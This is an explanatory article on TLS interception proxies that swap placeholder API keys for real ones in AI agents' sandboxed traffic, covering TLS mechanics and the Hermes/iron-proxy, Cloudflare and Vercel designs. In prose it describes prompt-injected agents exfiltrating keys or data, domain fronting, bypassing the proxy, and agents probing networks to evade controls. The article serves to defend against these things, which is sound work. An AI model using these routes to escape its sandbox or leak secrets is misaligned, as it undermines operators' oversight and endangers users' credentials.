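# TLS interception for inserting secrets into AI agents' encrypted traffic

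## Why a proxy must decrypt HTTPS before it can insert a secret

TLS interception means reading or changing encrypted web traffic between a program and a server. TLS (Transport Layer Security) encrypts HTTPS connections and lets the program check which server it has reached. An intercepting proxy accepts the program's encrypted connection in place of the server, decrypts the traffic, reads or alters it, and sends it to the real server over a second encrypted connection. Engineers also call this TLS termination, TLS inspection or man-in-the-middle proxying. Companies have long used it to inspect their employees' traffic, and some developers of AI agents now use it to prevent agents from accessing passwords and API keys.

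An AI agent is a language model with tools for running commands, editing files and calling web services. To call a service such as GitHub, which hosts software projects, a program usually sends an API key, a secret string that the service accepts as proof of the account. Anyone who copies the key can use the account. This is a particular problem for agents because files, web pages and user input can all influence their behaviour, a weakness known as prompt injection. Anthropic, the developer of the Claude models, describes this risk in its guide to securing agent deployments, giving the example of an agent that reads unusual instructions in a code repository's README file and may act on them in ways its operator did not anticipate. If the agent holds a working key, such instructions can lead it to send the key to an attacker's server, and the attacker can keep using the key after the agent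 has stopped.

A common remedy is to keep the key outside the sandbox, the restricted environment where the agent's commands run. The agent gets a harmless placeholder string, and a proxy outside the sandbox replaces it with the real key as each request leaves. Anthropic recommends the general pattern of a proxy that adds credentials to outgoing requests. The proxy can also restrict which addresses the agent may call and log every request. However, a misled agent can still send harmful requests through the proxy, which will attach the real key to them. The proxy must attach the key only to requests for the service that issued it. Otherwise, an attacker could have the agent send the placeholder to the attacker's own server and collect the real key there.

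Suppose the agent wants to look up the GitHub account it is working for. A program in the sandbox sends a request to https://api.github.com/user, and the text of the request is this:

```
GET /user HTTP/1.1
Host: api.github.com
Authorization: Bearer PLACEHOLDER
```

GitHub would refuse this request because PLACEHOLDER is not a valid key, so the proxy has to replace that word in the third line with the real key. Over plain HTTP, the proxy would receive the whole request as readable text and could edit it before passing it on. But the address begins with https, so the program encrypts the request before it leaves the sandbox.

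### The TLS handshake

Rescorla's *The Transport Layer Security (TLS) Protocol Version 1.3*, the 2026 edition of the standard, lists the properties that a TLS connection should have even if an attacker controls the entire network. The client can verify the server's identity, only the two endpoints can read the data, and nobody can modify the data without detection. A proxy between the sandbox and GitHub is in the same position as that attacker, so these protections apply to it regardless of its owner's intentions.

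The connection opens with a handshake, which begins with a key exchange. The client sends a ClientHello message containing a random number, the ciphers it supports and its half of the key exchange. The server answers with a ServerHello containing its own half. In the oldest form, Diffie–Hellman, both sides use a large prime *p* and a base *g*. The client picks a secret number *x* and sends *g^x* mod *p*, and the server picks a secret number *y* and sends *g^y* mod *p*. Each side raises the value it received to the power of its own secret number, which gives both of them *g^(xy)* mod *p*. An observer who copies both messages has no practical way to compute that value. Elliptic-curve versions work the same way. The client and server derive their encryption keys from the shared value and a hash of the messages so far, with a separate key for each direction. Everything after the ServerHello is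 encrypted.

At this point the client shares a secret with another party but has no evidence of who that is, since a proxy could have answered the ClientHello with its own *y*. The server therefore sends a certificate that ties the name api.github.com to a public key. The certificate is signed by a certificate authority (CA), an organization or program that vouches that a key belongs to a named host. Often a root CA signs the certificate of an intermediate CA, which in turn signs the host's certificate, so the server sends a chain of certificates, starting with the host's own, called the leaf certificate.

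Certificates are public, so a proxy could easily obtain GitHub's and send it to the client. The server must therefore follow its certificate with a CertificateVerify message, which contains a signature over a hash of the handshake up to that point. Only the holder of the matching private key can produce this signature. The hash covers both halves of the key exchange, so the signature is valid only for this connection. If a proxy substituted its own half and passed along GitHub's certificate and signature, the client would compute a different hash from the one GitHub signed. The signature would fail to verify, and the client would have to end the handshake. A final message, Finished, contains a keyed checksum over the entire handshake and confirms that both sides derived the same keys.

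The client checks whether the CA is in its trust store, the list of CAs that a program or operating system accepts. It follows the signatures from the leaf certificate up to a CA on the list, compares the name in the leaf with the name it requested, and checks the validity dates. If the chain leads to no CA on the list, the client ends the connection, and TLS defines the error "unknown_ca" for this case.

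Rescorla leaves most of the rules for validating certificates to other standards, and notes that the CAs at the top of the chain must be distributed to the client separately. They usually come with the operating system, the browser or the language runtime, and the machine's administrator can add more. One machine may hold several lists of trusted CAs. *About Certificates*, from the documentation of the open-source intercepting proxy mitmproxy, gives separate instructions for macOS, Firefox and Java, while the command-line program curl can take a CA file as an option. The client's check that it has reached GitHub therefore depends on a list that a local administrator can edit.

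### What the proxy sees in a CONNECT tunnel

A client that sends HTTPS through an ordinary proxy normally uses a CONNECT tunnel. It first sends the proxy a short request of its own, outside the TLS connection to GitHub:

```
CONNECT api.github.com:443 HTTP/1.1
```

The target of a CONNECT request is only a host and a port, as MDN's *CONNECT request method* explains. The proxy opens a connection to that host, reports success, and then forwards data blindly in both directions. The client performs its TLS handshake with GitHub through this tunnel. According to Cloudflare's *A Primer on Proxies* (2022), the proxy sees only TLS records, the blocks into which TLS divides its data, and cannot read their content because it does not have the keys.

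For the request to GitHub, the division looks like this:

| Item | Where it travels | Readable by the proxy? |
|---|---|---|
| Host and port | CONNECT line | Yes |
| Host name | SNI field of the ClientHello | Normally yes |
| Size and timing of the traffic | The records themselves | Yes |
| GitHub's certificate | Encrypted part of the handshake | No |
| Method and path, `GET /user` | Encrypted record | No |
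| `Authorization: Bearer PLACEHOLDER` | Encrypted record | No |
| GitHub's status code, headers and body | Encrypted records | No |

The client uses Server Name Indication (SNI) to name the host it wants at the start of the handshake, because one server at one IP address may handle many host names, each with its own certificate. No shared keys exist yet, so the name normally travels unencrypted. *TLS Encrypted Client Hello* (Rescorla, Oku and colleagues, 2026) specifies an extension that lets the client encrypt its ClientHello, including the SNI, under the server's public key. A proxy would still learn the host from the CONNECT line unless the client gave only an IP address there. The sizes are visible because TLS does not hide the length of the data it transmits, although either endpoint can pad its records to obscure them.

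The client supplies the host names in both the CONNECT line and the SNI field, and a proxy that cannot decrypt the traffic cannot check them against the request inside. Anthropic warns that sandboxed code may exploit this through domain fronting, in which the code names a permitted host on the outside and a different host in the encrypted request. This can work if the same provider's servers handle both hosts. A proxy that cannot decrypt can still block most connections to forbidden hosts, but it cannot insert a key. Anthropic says of a proxy carrying a CONNECT tunnel that "it cannot see or modify request contents without TLS interception".

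### Why the proxy cannot edit the encrypted bytes

The proxy only needs to change one word in the request, and it already has both the placeholder and the real key. It may even be able to guess where in the record the placeholder sits, since a program tends to build its requests the same way each time. Could it make the change without decrypting anything?

If TLS only encrypted traffic, a proxy could replace a placeholder with a secret without decrypting anything. The usual TLS 1.3 ciphers, AES-GCM and ChaCha20-Poly1305, encrypt text by combining it with a stream of key-dependent bytes using exclusive-or (⊕). Let *P* be the placeholder, *S* a real key of the same length, and *K* the part of the stream that covers the placeholder. The client sends *C* = *P* ⊕ *K*. The proxy can compute *C′* = *C* ⊕ *P* ⊕ *S* without having *K*. The server would then remove *K* from *C′* and read *S* in the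 Authorization header.

TLS 1.3 rules this out by permitting only ciphers that authenticate the data as well as encrypting it. Rescorla writes the operation on each record as:

```
AEADEncrypted = AEAD-Encrypt(write_key, nonce, additional_data, plaintext)
```

The encryption output includes an authentication tag, a short value that depends on the ciphertext, the write key, a nonce and additional data. The client derives the write key in the handshake and uses it only for the traffic it sends. The nonce, which must differ for every record, comes from the record's position in the sequence, and the additional data is the record's header, which includes its length. The server checks the tag during decryption, and if anything has changed, decryption fails and the server must close the connection with a "bad_record_mac" alert. If the proxy edited the encrypted request, GitHub would therefore close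 the connection without answering it.

The proxy would need the write key to compute a valid tag. Inserting a longer secret would also fail the tag check, because the tag covers the record's length. If the proxy dropped or added a record, the server would use the wrong nonce for the next record it received and fail to decrypt it.

### What interception requires

The proxy therefore needs the encryption keys, which only the two parties to a TLS handshake have. When the client connects directly to GitHub, those parties are the client and GitHub. The proxy can become a party only by splitting the connection into two, one from the client to the proxy and an upstream connection from the proxy to GitHub.

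The client now performs its TLS handshake with the proxy, but it still accepts only a certificate for api.github.com. The proxy cannot use GitHub's own certificate because it lacks the matching private key, which it needs to produce the CertificateVerify signature. It therefore generates a key pair, creates a leaf certificate for api.github.com containing the public key, and signs the certificate with the key of a CA it controls. The client will reject this certificate unless that CA is in its trust store. According to mitmproxy, the CA system exists to prevent exactly this kind of impersonation, and the way around it is to register the proxy with the client as a trusted CA.

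Anthropic lists the same requirement for any agent that must reach arbitrary HTTPS services through a proxy that changes its requests. The operator runs the proxy outside the agent's container, installs the proxy's CA certificate in the agent's trust store, and routes the traffic to the proxy. If a program ignores proxy settings, the operator can redirect its traffic at the network level, but the CA certificate is still needed. Interception is unnecessary for a program that can be configured to send requests directly to the proxy as if it were the service, but many programs have no such setting.

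With the CA certificate in place, the request to GitHub proceeds as follows:

1. The client sends `CONNECT api.github.com:443` to the proxy, and the proxy reports success without opening a tunnel.
2. The client starts a TLS handshake and gives api.github.com as the SNI.
3. The proxy makes a leaf certificate for that name, signs it with its CA's signing key, and completes the handshake in GitHub's place.
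4. The client finds the proxy's CA in its trust store, accepts the certificate, and sends the request with PLACEHOLDER in the header, under keys that it shares with the proxy.
5. The proxy decrypts the request and replaces PLACEHOLDER with the real key.
6. The proxy sends the edited request to GitHub over the upstream connection, under keys that it shares with GitHub.
7. GitHub's answer returns to the proxy, which decrypts it, encrypts it again for the client and passes it on.

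The proxy can also connect to the real server before it completes the client's handshake, for instance when the CONNECT line gives only an IP address. It can wait for the SNI, pause the handshake, connect to the server, and copy the host names from the real certificate into the one it makes. The mitmproxy documentation describes this method.

The sandbox needs only the CA's public certificate, and the signing key stays with the proxy. mitmproxy stores the certificate and private key together in one file, and the certificate alone in another for distribution to clients. Keeping the key out of the sandbox is important because a CA in a trust store can normally sign certificates for any host, not just GitHub. Anyone who obtained the key could make certificates for a bank or an email provider, and every program that uses that trust store would accept them.

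The proxy must also verify GitHub's certificate against its own trust store, which the client can no longer do because it sees only the proxy's certificate. Rescorla requires any device that terminates a TLS connection to act as a proper server towards the client and as a proper client towards the server, "including verifying the original server's certificate". The device must also compose its own ClientHello, using only parameters it understands, rather than copy the client's. Rescorla adds that the security analysis of TLS applies to the two connections separately, and leaves the safe deployment of such a device outside the standard. If the proxy skips the check on GitHub's certificate, the client has no way to notice, and an impostor answering in GitHub's place would receive the request with the real key in the header.

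## iron-proxy in Hermes Agent: one request from placeholder to real key

Hermes Agent, an open-source AI agent from the company Nous Research, writes code and does other tasks by running commands in a terminal. Users can run these commands on their own machine, on a remote machine over SSH, in a Docker container, or on Daytona, Modal or Singularity (Nous Research, *Hermes Agent*). A Docker container is an isolated environment with its own files and processes, and the machine that runs it is the host.

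Normally the container holds the user's real API keys in configuration files or environment variables, which are named strings that programs read as settings. Nous Research's *Egress credential-injection proxy (iron-proxy)* describes an optional feature that keeps the keys on the host. Hermes puts placeholders in the container and runs iron-proxy, a separate open-source program from the developer ironsh, on the host. The proxy intercepts the container's HTTPS traffic and replaces the placeholders with the real keys.

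The feature covers only programs inside the container. Hermes itself runs on the host and uses the real keys directly when it calls the language model that drives the agent. Requests go through the proxy when, for example, the agent writes a Python script that calls a model API and runs that script in the container. The request below comes from such a script and goes to OpenRouter, a service that offers models from many companies through one API.

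### What Hermes prepares

The user first runs a set-up command, which creates a CA on the host. The CA's signing key never enters a container and is stored in a file that only the user's account can read. The command then searches the user's settings for model provider keys and generates a placeholder for each one. Nous Research calls these placeholders proxy tokens. A file on the host records which placeholder stands for which key.

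Another command starts iron-proxy and passes it the real keys in environment variables. Nous Research's contributor guide, *Egress proxy internals*, forbids copying the host's whole environment into iron-proxy. It receives only the keys it has to insert and a few ordinary settings, so the user's unrelated secrets stay out of its memory.

When Hermes creates a container, it copies in the CA's public certificate as a read-only file and sets a group of environment variables. These are some of them:

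```
OPENROUTER_API_KEY=hermes-proxy-openrouter-…
HTTPS_PROXY=http://host.docker.internal:9090
HTTP_PROXY=http://host.docker.internal:9091
NO_PROXY=127.0.0.1,localhost,::1
SSL_CERT_FILE=/etc/ssl/certs/hermes-egress-ca.crt
```

The first line puts the placeholder under the name that OpenRouter's client libraries already look for, so existing programs run without changes. Inside the container, host.docker.internal refers to the host. NO_PROXY exempts addresses inside the container from the proxy, so the agent can still test a web server it has just written. The last line gives some programs the location of the CA certificate.

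HTTPS_PROXY is only a convention. Many HTTP clients, including curl and Python's httpx library, read the variable and send their requests to the address in it. The variable does not block any other route out of the container.

### The request, step by step

The script reads the placeholder from OPENROUTER_API_KEY and puts it in the Authorization header of a POST request to https://openrouter.ai/v1/chat/completions. Its HTTP library finds HTTPS_PROXY and sends `CONNECT openrouter.ai:443` to port 9090 on the host. iron-proxy listens for CONNECT requests on that port and for plain HTTP on port 9091, so Hermes sets two variables. Nous Research found that if a client sends a CONNECT request to port 9091, iron-proxy forwards it as if it were an ordinary request, and the request fails.

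iron-proxy then checks the host name against an allowlist. Hermes's default list covers ten model providers, among them OpenRouter, OpenAI, Anthropic and Google. For any other host, iron-proxy returns the HTTP error 403 before any data leaves the host, and names the forbidden host in the error so that the agent can report it. The default list contains neither GitHub nor any package repository, so a command that downloads a Python library would fail until the user added the right hosts.

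Nous Research writes that `*.example.com` does not match example.com itself, while ironsh's *iron-proxy* states that it does, so users who add hosts with a wildcard should test the result.

Because openrouter.ai is on the list, iron-proxy answers the script's TLS handshake with a leaf certificate it generated. In ironsh's sample configuration, these certificates last 72 hours, and the proxy keeps up to 1,000 of them in memory for later connections to the same hosts. The script's HTTP library finds the CA in the file Hermes supplied, accepts the certificate, and sends the request.

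Now iron-proxy can read the request. It applies a series of operations, which ironsh calls transforms, in a fixed order. One of them, named "secrets", searches the request for placeholders. Each rule specifies a placeholder, the source of the real key, the headers to search and the hosts for which the swap is allowed. For OpenRouter, the rule covers the Authorization header. Anthropic's API expects its key in the x-api-key header, and Google's accepts one in a header or in the URL, so Hermes has separate rules for them. Here the placeholder, header and host all match, so iron-proxy replaces the placeholder with the real key.

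The host condition ties each key to the service that issued it. If the script sent the OpenRouter placeholder to api.openai.com, which is also on the allowlist, OpenAI would receive only the placeholder. The condition also limits which servers could send the real key back to the container. A server that repeats request headers in its response would return the key unless the proxy removed it, so an operator who adds a swap rule for a new service has to know that the service does not repeat them.

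Any transform that runs after the swap handles the real key. For example, iron-proxy can use a language model to check whether a request complies with a written policy. ironsh recommends running this check before the swap, so that the company running the model sees only the placeholder. It also recommends recording request bodies before the swap if the operator has told iron-proxy to look for placeholders in them, because the log would otherwise contain real keys in plain text.

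iron-proxy then opens the upstream connection to OpenRouter. It first compares the IP address behind the host name with a list of forbidden ranges, which include the host itself, private networks and 169.254.169.254, the address where cloud machines obtain information about themselves and often temporary credentials. The allowlist alone would not protect these addresses. An attacker who controls the DNS records of an allowed host name could point it at one of them. iron-proxy makes this check at the moment of connecting, so a DNS record that changes after the allowlist check does not get around it.

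OpenRouter receives the request with a valid key, and its response returns to the script through the proxy. iron-proxy logs each request, including those it refuses, as a line of JSON, a structured text format. ironsh's sample entry gives the host, method, path, status code and duration, as well as the name of the secret and the header that contained it, but not the secret's value. In the version of iron-proxy that Hermes installs, these entries go in the same file as the program's general messages. Hermes also creates a separate audit file for later versions, but it stays empty for now, and Nous Research warns users not to point their monitoring at it.

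### How programs in the container come to accept the CA

Programs in one container may use different trust stores, so Hermes sets one variable for each common library or tool, all pointing to the same certificate file.

| Variable | Program that reads it | Effect on the trust store |
|---|---|---|
| `REQUESTS_CA_BUNDLE` | Python's requests library | Replaces it |
| `SSL_CERT_FILE` | Python's ssl module and OpenSSL | Replaces it |
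| `CURL_CA_BUNDLE` | curl | Replaces it |
| `NODE_EXTRA_CA_CERTS` | Node.js | Adds to it |

OpenSSL is a widely used encryption library, and Node.js runs JavaScript programs outside a browser.

Whether the proxy's CA replaces the usual public CAs or is added to them matters when a program connects directly to a server. OpenRouter's genuine certificate comes from a public CA. A Python program under Hermes trusts only the proxy's CA, so it rejects that certificate and ends the connection. It can complete a handshake only with iron-proxy or with someone who has stolen the signing key of the proxy's CA. Node.js trusts the proxy's CA as well as the usual public ones, so a Node.js program that connects directly accepts OpenRouter's certificate and continues.

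Nous Research lists this as a known limitation. To narrow it, Hermes also passes Node.js the option `--use-openssl-ca`, which makes Node.js use OpenSSL's trust store, the one that SSL_CERT_FILE replaces. The option has no effect on code that supplies its own list of CAs. Nous Research advises users who depend on a sandbox's isolation not to run untrusted Node.js code there if it opens its own network connections.

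Replacing the trust store catches mistakes more reliably than it stops attacks. If an ordinary Python program accidentally bypasses the proxy, it stops with a certificate error instead of silently connecting. But the program itself checks the certificate, and an agent that writes its own code can choose which CAs that code accepts. This is true in any language, so closing the Node.js gap would not confine an agent that tries to avoid the proxy.

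### What a program gets by going around the proxy

Some programs don't support HTTPS_PROXY, and a misled agent might ignore it on purpose. Hermes's Docker feature does not stop either from connecting directly, and Nous Research lists such connections among the things the feature does not protect against.

Such a program still has only the placeholder. If it reaches OpenRouter directly, even over a valid TLS connection, it sends the placeholder as its key, and OpenRouter rejects the request because the placeholder belongs to no account. The real key stays on the host, and the program can't obtain it by choosing a different route.

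The placeholder is also of little use to an attacker who copies it, because it works only at iron-proxy. On Linux, iron-proxy listens on an address internal to Docker, and on macOS and Windows it listens on the host's loopback address, so an attacker elsewhere on the network could not use a copied placeholder. Other containers on the same Docker network can reach the Linux address, so they could use a leaked placeholder.

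The allowlist, the forbidden IP ranges and the log apply only to traffic that passes through iron-proxy, so a program that connects directly avoids all three. It can send the user's source code, or any other file in the container, to a server that is not on the allowlist, and iron-proxy would have no record of it. If the host runs in a cloud and nothing else blocks the connection, the program might also reach 169.254.169.254 and obtain credentials that the swap does not protect, because Hermes never replaced them with placeholders.

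Keeping this control requires a rule outside the container that blocks all traffic except traffic to the proxy. ironsh recommends adding such rules for stronger enforcement. Slipper's *Minimum Viable Agent Security* describes how the team behind iron-proxy does this for its own agent, Scout, which is built on Hermes. Scout has a rented machine to itself, and iron-proxy runs on another. The cloud provider's firewall lets Scout's machine connect only to the proxy, for web traffic and DNS lookups, so a program there that ignores the proxy cannot connect to anything.

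Slipper advises against running Hermes's commands in a Docker container because he thinks agents will find any way out that exists. The team has seen agents scan the internal network for other machines, try to log in to a remote machine and send requests from there, and try several DNS services in turn. This is first-hand evidence that agents look for ways around network controls, but Slipper gives no counts and does not name the models or the tasks. The team also offers paid help with this kind of security. His account supports having a network rule, but it does not show how often a Docker container on its own would fail.

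Nous Research notes that an agent limited to approved hosts could still hide data in the body of a request to one of them, such as api.openai.com. If the request used an attacker's API key, the data could end up in the attacker's account at a service the user trusts. iron-proxy has an option, off by default, that rejects any request to a given host unless it contains the placeholder, so a program cannot substitute another key. Operators can also allow only certain methods and paths. For example, Scout's rules let it edit the release pages of one GitHub repository, although Slipper says the underlying key, of GitHub's classic type, could write to every repository its owner can.

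simedw (2026), in *How to force AI agents to use an egress proxy*, sets out why users do not simply cut off the network. Agents need it to call the model provider, read documentation and copy public repositories, and each of these uses adds hosts to the allowlist. A longer list makes the agent more useful and gives a misled agent more places to send data.

### Refusing to start without the proxy

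The feature is off by default. Once a user turns it on, Hermes refuses to create a Docker container if iron-proxy is not running, which engineers call failing closed. If Hermes instead started the container the old way, with the real keys inside and direct access to the internet, the user might go on believing that the keys were safe. Users can choose the old behaviour by setting `enforce_on_docker` to false, in which case Hermes also logs a warning.

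Hermes also stops if the user's own Docker settings already define HTTPS_PROXY, one of the CA variables or OPENROUTER_API_KEY, and it names the conflicting variables. Using those values could let the container skip the proxy or receive the real key. Hermes does the same if the user passes extra Docker arguments that change the proxy settings or the network, because these come after its own arguments and could override them. It also marks its long-lived containers so that a new session does not reuse one from before the user enabled the proxy, which might still hold real keys.

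The real keys can come from Bitwarden Secrets Manager, a service for storing passwords and keys, instead of the user's local settings. With Bitwarden, iron-proxy fetches the current keys each time it starts. If one is missing, Hermes refuses to start iron-proxy rather than fall back on an older copy from the local settings. Nous Research reasons that people choose Bitwarden to replace keys regularly, and silently using old ones would defeat that purpose.

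These checks run at the start. If iron-proxy stops later, a running container keeps its placeholders and proxy settings, so programs that use the proxy get connection errors and the keys stay on the host. Some secrets also get past the checks. Hermes warns about credentials that programs use to sign requests, which a header swap cannot handle, but leaves them in the container. It does not inspect credential files that the user chooses to share with the container.

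### Versions and remaining limits

Nous Research's description of the feature is undated, but it covers iron-proxy v0.39.0, and one of its examples contains a file name with the date 24 May 2026. ironsh's *Releases* lists v0.42.0 on 8 June 2026 and v0.45.0 on 16 June. Some features in the newer versions would suit Hermes. From v0.42.0, iron-proxy can read a key from a file and pick up a new value while it runs, whereas Hermes has to restart the proxy when a key changes. From v0.43.0, operators can switch off iron-proxy's built-in DNS server, which programs that use HTTPS_PROXY do not need. Releasebot's *Nous Research Release Notes* (2026) lists a test build of Hermes v0.23.4 on 25 November 2026, so Hermes may by now install a newer iron-proxy.

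As described, the feature works only with the Docker backend. Containers on Modal and Daytona, and commands over SSH or in Singularity, receive neither the proxy settings nor the CA certificate. Nous Research estimates that each additional backend would need roughly 150 lines of code, about as much as Docker's, to set the variables, deliver the certificate and detect conflicting settings. A sandbox on someone else's servers would also need a route to the proxy, because by default iron-proxy listens only on addresses that other machines cannot reach.

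The CA is the other weak point. Its certificate is valid for ten years, and Hermes has no command for replacing it, so the user has to generate a new one by hand. Every container that Hermes starts with the feature enabled receives this certificate, so all of them depend on one signing key on the host.

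## Cloudflare and Vercel sandboxes: a separate authority for each sandbox

Cloudflare and Vercel rent out sandboxes on their own servers, and both insert secrets by intercepting TLS. They create a new CA for each sandbox that lasts only as long as the sandbox runs, whereas Hermes gives all its containers the same CA, valid for ten years. Someone who stole a sandbox's signing key could impersonate web servers only to that sandbox, and only until it stopped.

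Both companies also capture traffic in the network, so it reaches the proxy even if a program ignores HTTPS_PROXY. Cloudflare can decrypt every HTTPS request and pass it to the customer's code, while Vercel decrypts only connections to domains where the customer has set a rule that requires it.

### How the network captures a connection

In transparent interception, a program opens an ordinary connection and the network delivers it to a proxy. Suppose curl in the sandbox requests https://api.github.com/user. It resolves the name to an IP address and opens a TCP connection to port 443 there. A redirection rule sends the packets to the proxy, which accepts the connection in GitHub's place. curl sends no CONNECT request because it isn't configured to use a proxy.

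Freestyle's *Inspect sandbox traffic with mitmproxy* describes a simple version for the company's sandboxes. All traffic leaves through a second machine, where nftables, Linux's packet filter, redirects TCP ports 80 and 443 to mitmproxy. The second machine also rejects UDP traffic on port 443, which HTTP/3 uses, so clients that try HTTP/3 fall back to HTTPS over TCP, which mitmproxy can inspect.

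Vercel's firewall captures more traffic. Tuttle (2026) explains in *A sandbox without a network boundary is only half a sandbox* that Linux redirects every outbound TCP connection and DNS query to the firewall, which records the original destination. The firewall runs on the host, while the sandbox is a microVM, a small virtual machine with its own operating-system kernel. Code inside the sandbox therefore cannot switch the firewall off, even with administrator rights.

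Programs in the sandbox still have to trust the proxy's CA. A redirected connection gives the proxy only an IP address and a port, without the host name a CONNECT line would include, so the proxy has to read the host name from the SNI.

### Cloudflare: a Worker adds the key

Cloudflare's *Dynamic, identity-aware, and secure Sandbox auth* (2026) introduced outbound Workers in April. A Worker is a small program, often in JavaScript, that a customer writes and Cloudflare runs on its servers. An outbound Worker handles the requests that leave a sandbox. A customer could write this handler for the GitHub request:

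```
MySandbox.outboundByHost = {
  "api.github.com": (request, env) => {
    const edited = new Request(request);
    edited.headers.set("Authorization", `Bearer ${env.GITHUB_TOKEN}`);
    return fetch(edited);
  },
};
```

The real key, GITHUB_TOKEN, stays in the Worker's settings. The request then proceeds as follows:

1. The network delivers curl's connection to a sidecar, a helper process that Cloudflare runs beside the sandbox.
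2. The sidecar reads api.github.com from the SNI, makes a leaf certificate for that name and signs it with the sandbox's own CA.
3. curl finds the CA in its trust store, completes the handshake and sends `GET /user` without a key.
4. The sidecar decrypts the request and calls the Worker, which runs on the same machine.
5. The Worker sets the Authorization header, and its `fetch` call sends the request to GitHub.

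The design needs no placeholder because the Worker adds the whole header. Some tools won't start without a key, but the customer can give them any string, which the handler overwrites.

Cloudflare states that the key used to sign certificates never leaves the sidecar and that sidecars never share keys. The customer's Worker has the GitHub key and sees the decrypted requests, so a mistake in its code could leak either, but it could not leak the signing key, which the Worker does not have. Customers can check that two sandboxes have different CA certificates, but they have to rely on Cloudflare's word for where the private keys are.

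The Worker also receives the identifier of the sandbox that made the request, which it can use to look up that sandbox's own key in KV, Cloudflare's key-value store. If ten agents work for ten users, each agent's requests can carry only its own user's key. The sandbox does not need a token to prove its identity, because the whole exchange takes place on one machine.

Sandboxes intercept traffic by default, according to Cloudflare's *Handle outbound traffic*. At startup, the sandbox software looks for the system's list of CAs where common Linux distributions keep it, and sets the trust-store variables for programs such as Node.js and Git. Cloudflare calls this a best effort. In Cloudflare's plain containers, the customer has to turn interception on. Cloudflare warns in its guide to these containers against building the CA certificate into the image, the template from which new containers start,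 because the CA does not exist until the container runs. The start-up command has to install the certificate before the application opens its first connection.

### Vercel: decryption only where a rule needs it

Vercel's *Sandbox firewall* describes a policy that combines a list of allowed domains with optional rules for each. A "transform" rule changes request headers. Vercel uses these rules to insert credentials, which it calls credentials brokering. A forwarding rule sends requests to a proxy that the customer runs. A direct-response rule makes the firewall answer the request itself, for instance with an error. The firewall decrypts only connections to domains that have at least one of these rules.

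The following policy allows two domains, GitHub's API and the registry from which the npm tool downloads JavaScript packages. Only GitHub has a rule.

```
{
  "allow": {
    "api.github.com": [
      { "transform": [
          { "headers": { "Authorization": "Bearer REAL_KEY" } }
      ] }
    ],
    "registry.npmjs.org": []
  }
}
```

When curl requests https://api.github.com/user, it first looks up the name, and the firewall checks the lookup against the list of domains. curl then opens a connection, and Linux redirects it to the firewall. The firewall reads the SNI, finds api.github.com on the list and checks that the policy does not forbid the destination address. Because the domain has a rule, the firewall completes the TLS handshake itself with a leaf certificate from the sandbox's CA. It decrypts the request, sets the Authorization header to the real key and sends the request to GitHub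 over a new TLS connection.

When npm connects to registry.npmjs.org, the firewall performs the same checks, up to and including the SNI. This domain has no rule, so the firewall connects to the registry and forwards npm's ClientHello. npm completes the handshake directly with the registry, which presents its real certificate, and the firewall only relays encrypted bytes. The SNI reveals that the sandbox is connecting to the registry, but encryption hides which packages it downloads.

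The firewall can choose between these two courses because the ClientHello comes first and is readable. It can hold the message while it checks the policy, then either answer it or pass it on. Once it has passed the message on, it can't join the connection, for the same reasons that a proxy can't read a CONNECT tunnel. It must therefore decide by domain alone, before it sees any of the request.

Vercel also lets a rule apply only to certain paths, methods, query parameters or headers. These are all encrypted in transit, so a rule for a single path requires the firewall to decrypt every connection to that domain.

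These conditions do not block anything alone. If a policy inserts a key into POST requests whose path starts with /v1/, a request to any other path still reaches the service, but without the inserted key. To block such requests, the customer must add a final rule that returns a 403 error for everything else. This rule must come last because the firewall uses the first rule that matches, so placing it first would block every request.

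The order matters for data theft too. Under Hermes, a misled agent could send data to an approved service with an attacker's API key. Vercel explains in an announcement of header injection that the firewall replaces any header with the same name as the injected one, which prevents the sandbox from using its own key. However, a request that doesn't match the rule keeps whatever key the program put in it, so the whole domain is protected only if the rule has no conditions or if a refusal of all other requests follows it.

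With a forwarding rule, the customer's own proxy can inspect requests, log them or remove sensitive fields. Vercel attaches a signed token that identifies the team, project and sandbox behind each request. The proxy has to check the token's signature and expiry date, and that Vercel issued it for this proxy's address. Otherwise, it might accept a token meant for another proxy. The customer can then use the sandbox's identity to choose a key with narrow permissions, much as a Cloudflare Worker does with the sandbox identifier.

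In both services, the customer's trusted code can change the rules while the sandbox runs. For example, it can allow requests to GitHub and add a key to them while the agent clones a repository, then remove the key or cut off the network before running code that the agent wrote. This limits how long a misled agent can make authenticated requests through the proxy. In Cloudflare's version, the next request on an open connection uses the new handler, so the agent cannot keep its access by holding a connection open.

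### What selective decryption gains and loses

With selective decryption, most of the sandbox's traffic is never in the firewall's memory as plain text. A firewall bug that exposed request contents, or a log that recorded too much, would leak only traffic to domains with rules. Vercel runs the machine that hosts the sandbox, so selective decryption does not protect the customer from Vercel.

It also means that fewer requests fail when a program does not accept the CA. Vercel's *Runtimes* gives an example. An agent can run Docker containers inside its sandbox, but each container has its own files and trust store and does not inherit the sandbox's CA. Under the policy above, a request from such a container to api.github.com would fail because the container does not trust the CA that issued the firewall's certificate. A package download from registry.npmjs.org would still work, since the container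 receives the registry's own certificate. To fix the GitHub request, the user has to mount the CA certificate into the container and update its trust store.

Programs in a Vercel sandbox need to trust the public CAs as well as the sandbox's own CA because they receive certificates issued by both. Vercel therefore can't replace the trust store with a single CA, as Hermes does for Python programs, but it needs that safeguard less because the host redirects the traffic.

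Vercel's firewall can forward encrypted bytes without parsing them, so it also supports programs that don't use HTTP. Vercel built it around the SNI because sending all traffic through an HTTP proxy would break the protocols of the Redis and Postgres databases.

The main drawback is that the firewall can't inspect encrypted traffic to an allowed domain that has no rule. In the example, the agent needs the npm registry only to download packages, but the registry also accepts uploads. A misled agent could use an attacker's account to publish the user's source code there as a package, and the firewall would allow the connection because the domain is approved.

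A proxy that decrypts everything can prevent this. One of Cloudflare's example handlers covers all hosts and logs and refuses any request other than a GET, the method for fetching data. This blocks ordinary uploads, although an agent can still hide a small amount of data in the address of a GET request. Vercel's customers can get a similar check for a domain by adding a rule, even when they have no key to insert there. Adding one is probably worthwhile for any domain that accepts uploads from anyone.

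The SNI can differ from the host named inside the encrypted request, so a domain without a rule may also let the sandbox reach other sites on the same servers.

Decryption also changes which software checks the server's certificate. npm checks the registry's certificate itself, but the firewall checks GitHub's, or in Cloudflare's case, the software that makes the Worker's outgoing connection does. The inserted key is safe only if the proxy does this check correctly, and neither Vercel's firewall guide nor Cloudflare's April post explains how the check works.

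### Connections that the rules miss

Some customers want an agent to reach the whole internet and still use inserted keys at a few services. Vercel supports this with a catch-all rule, `*`, alongside the rules for individual domains. Vercel states that under a catch-all rule, connections without SNI pass through unmodified, such as SSH connections or TLS connections from a client that omits the field.

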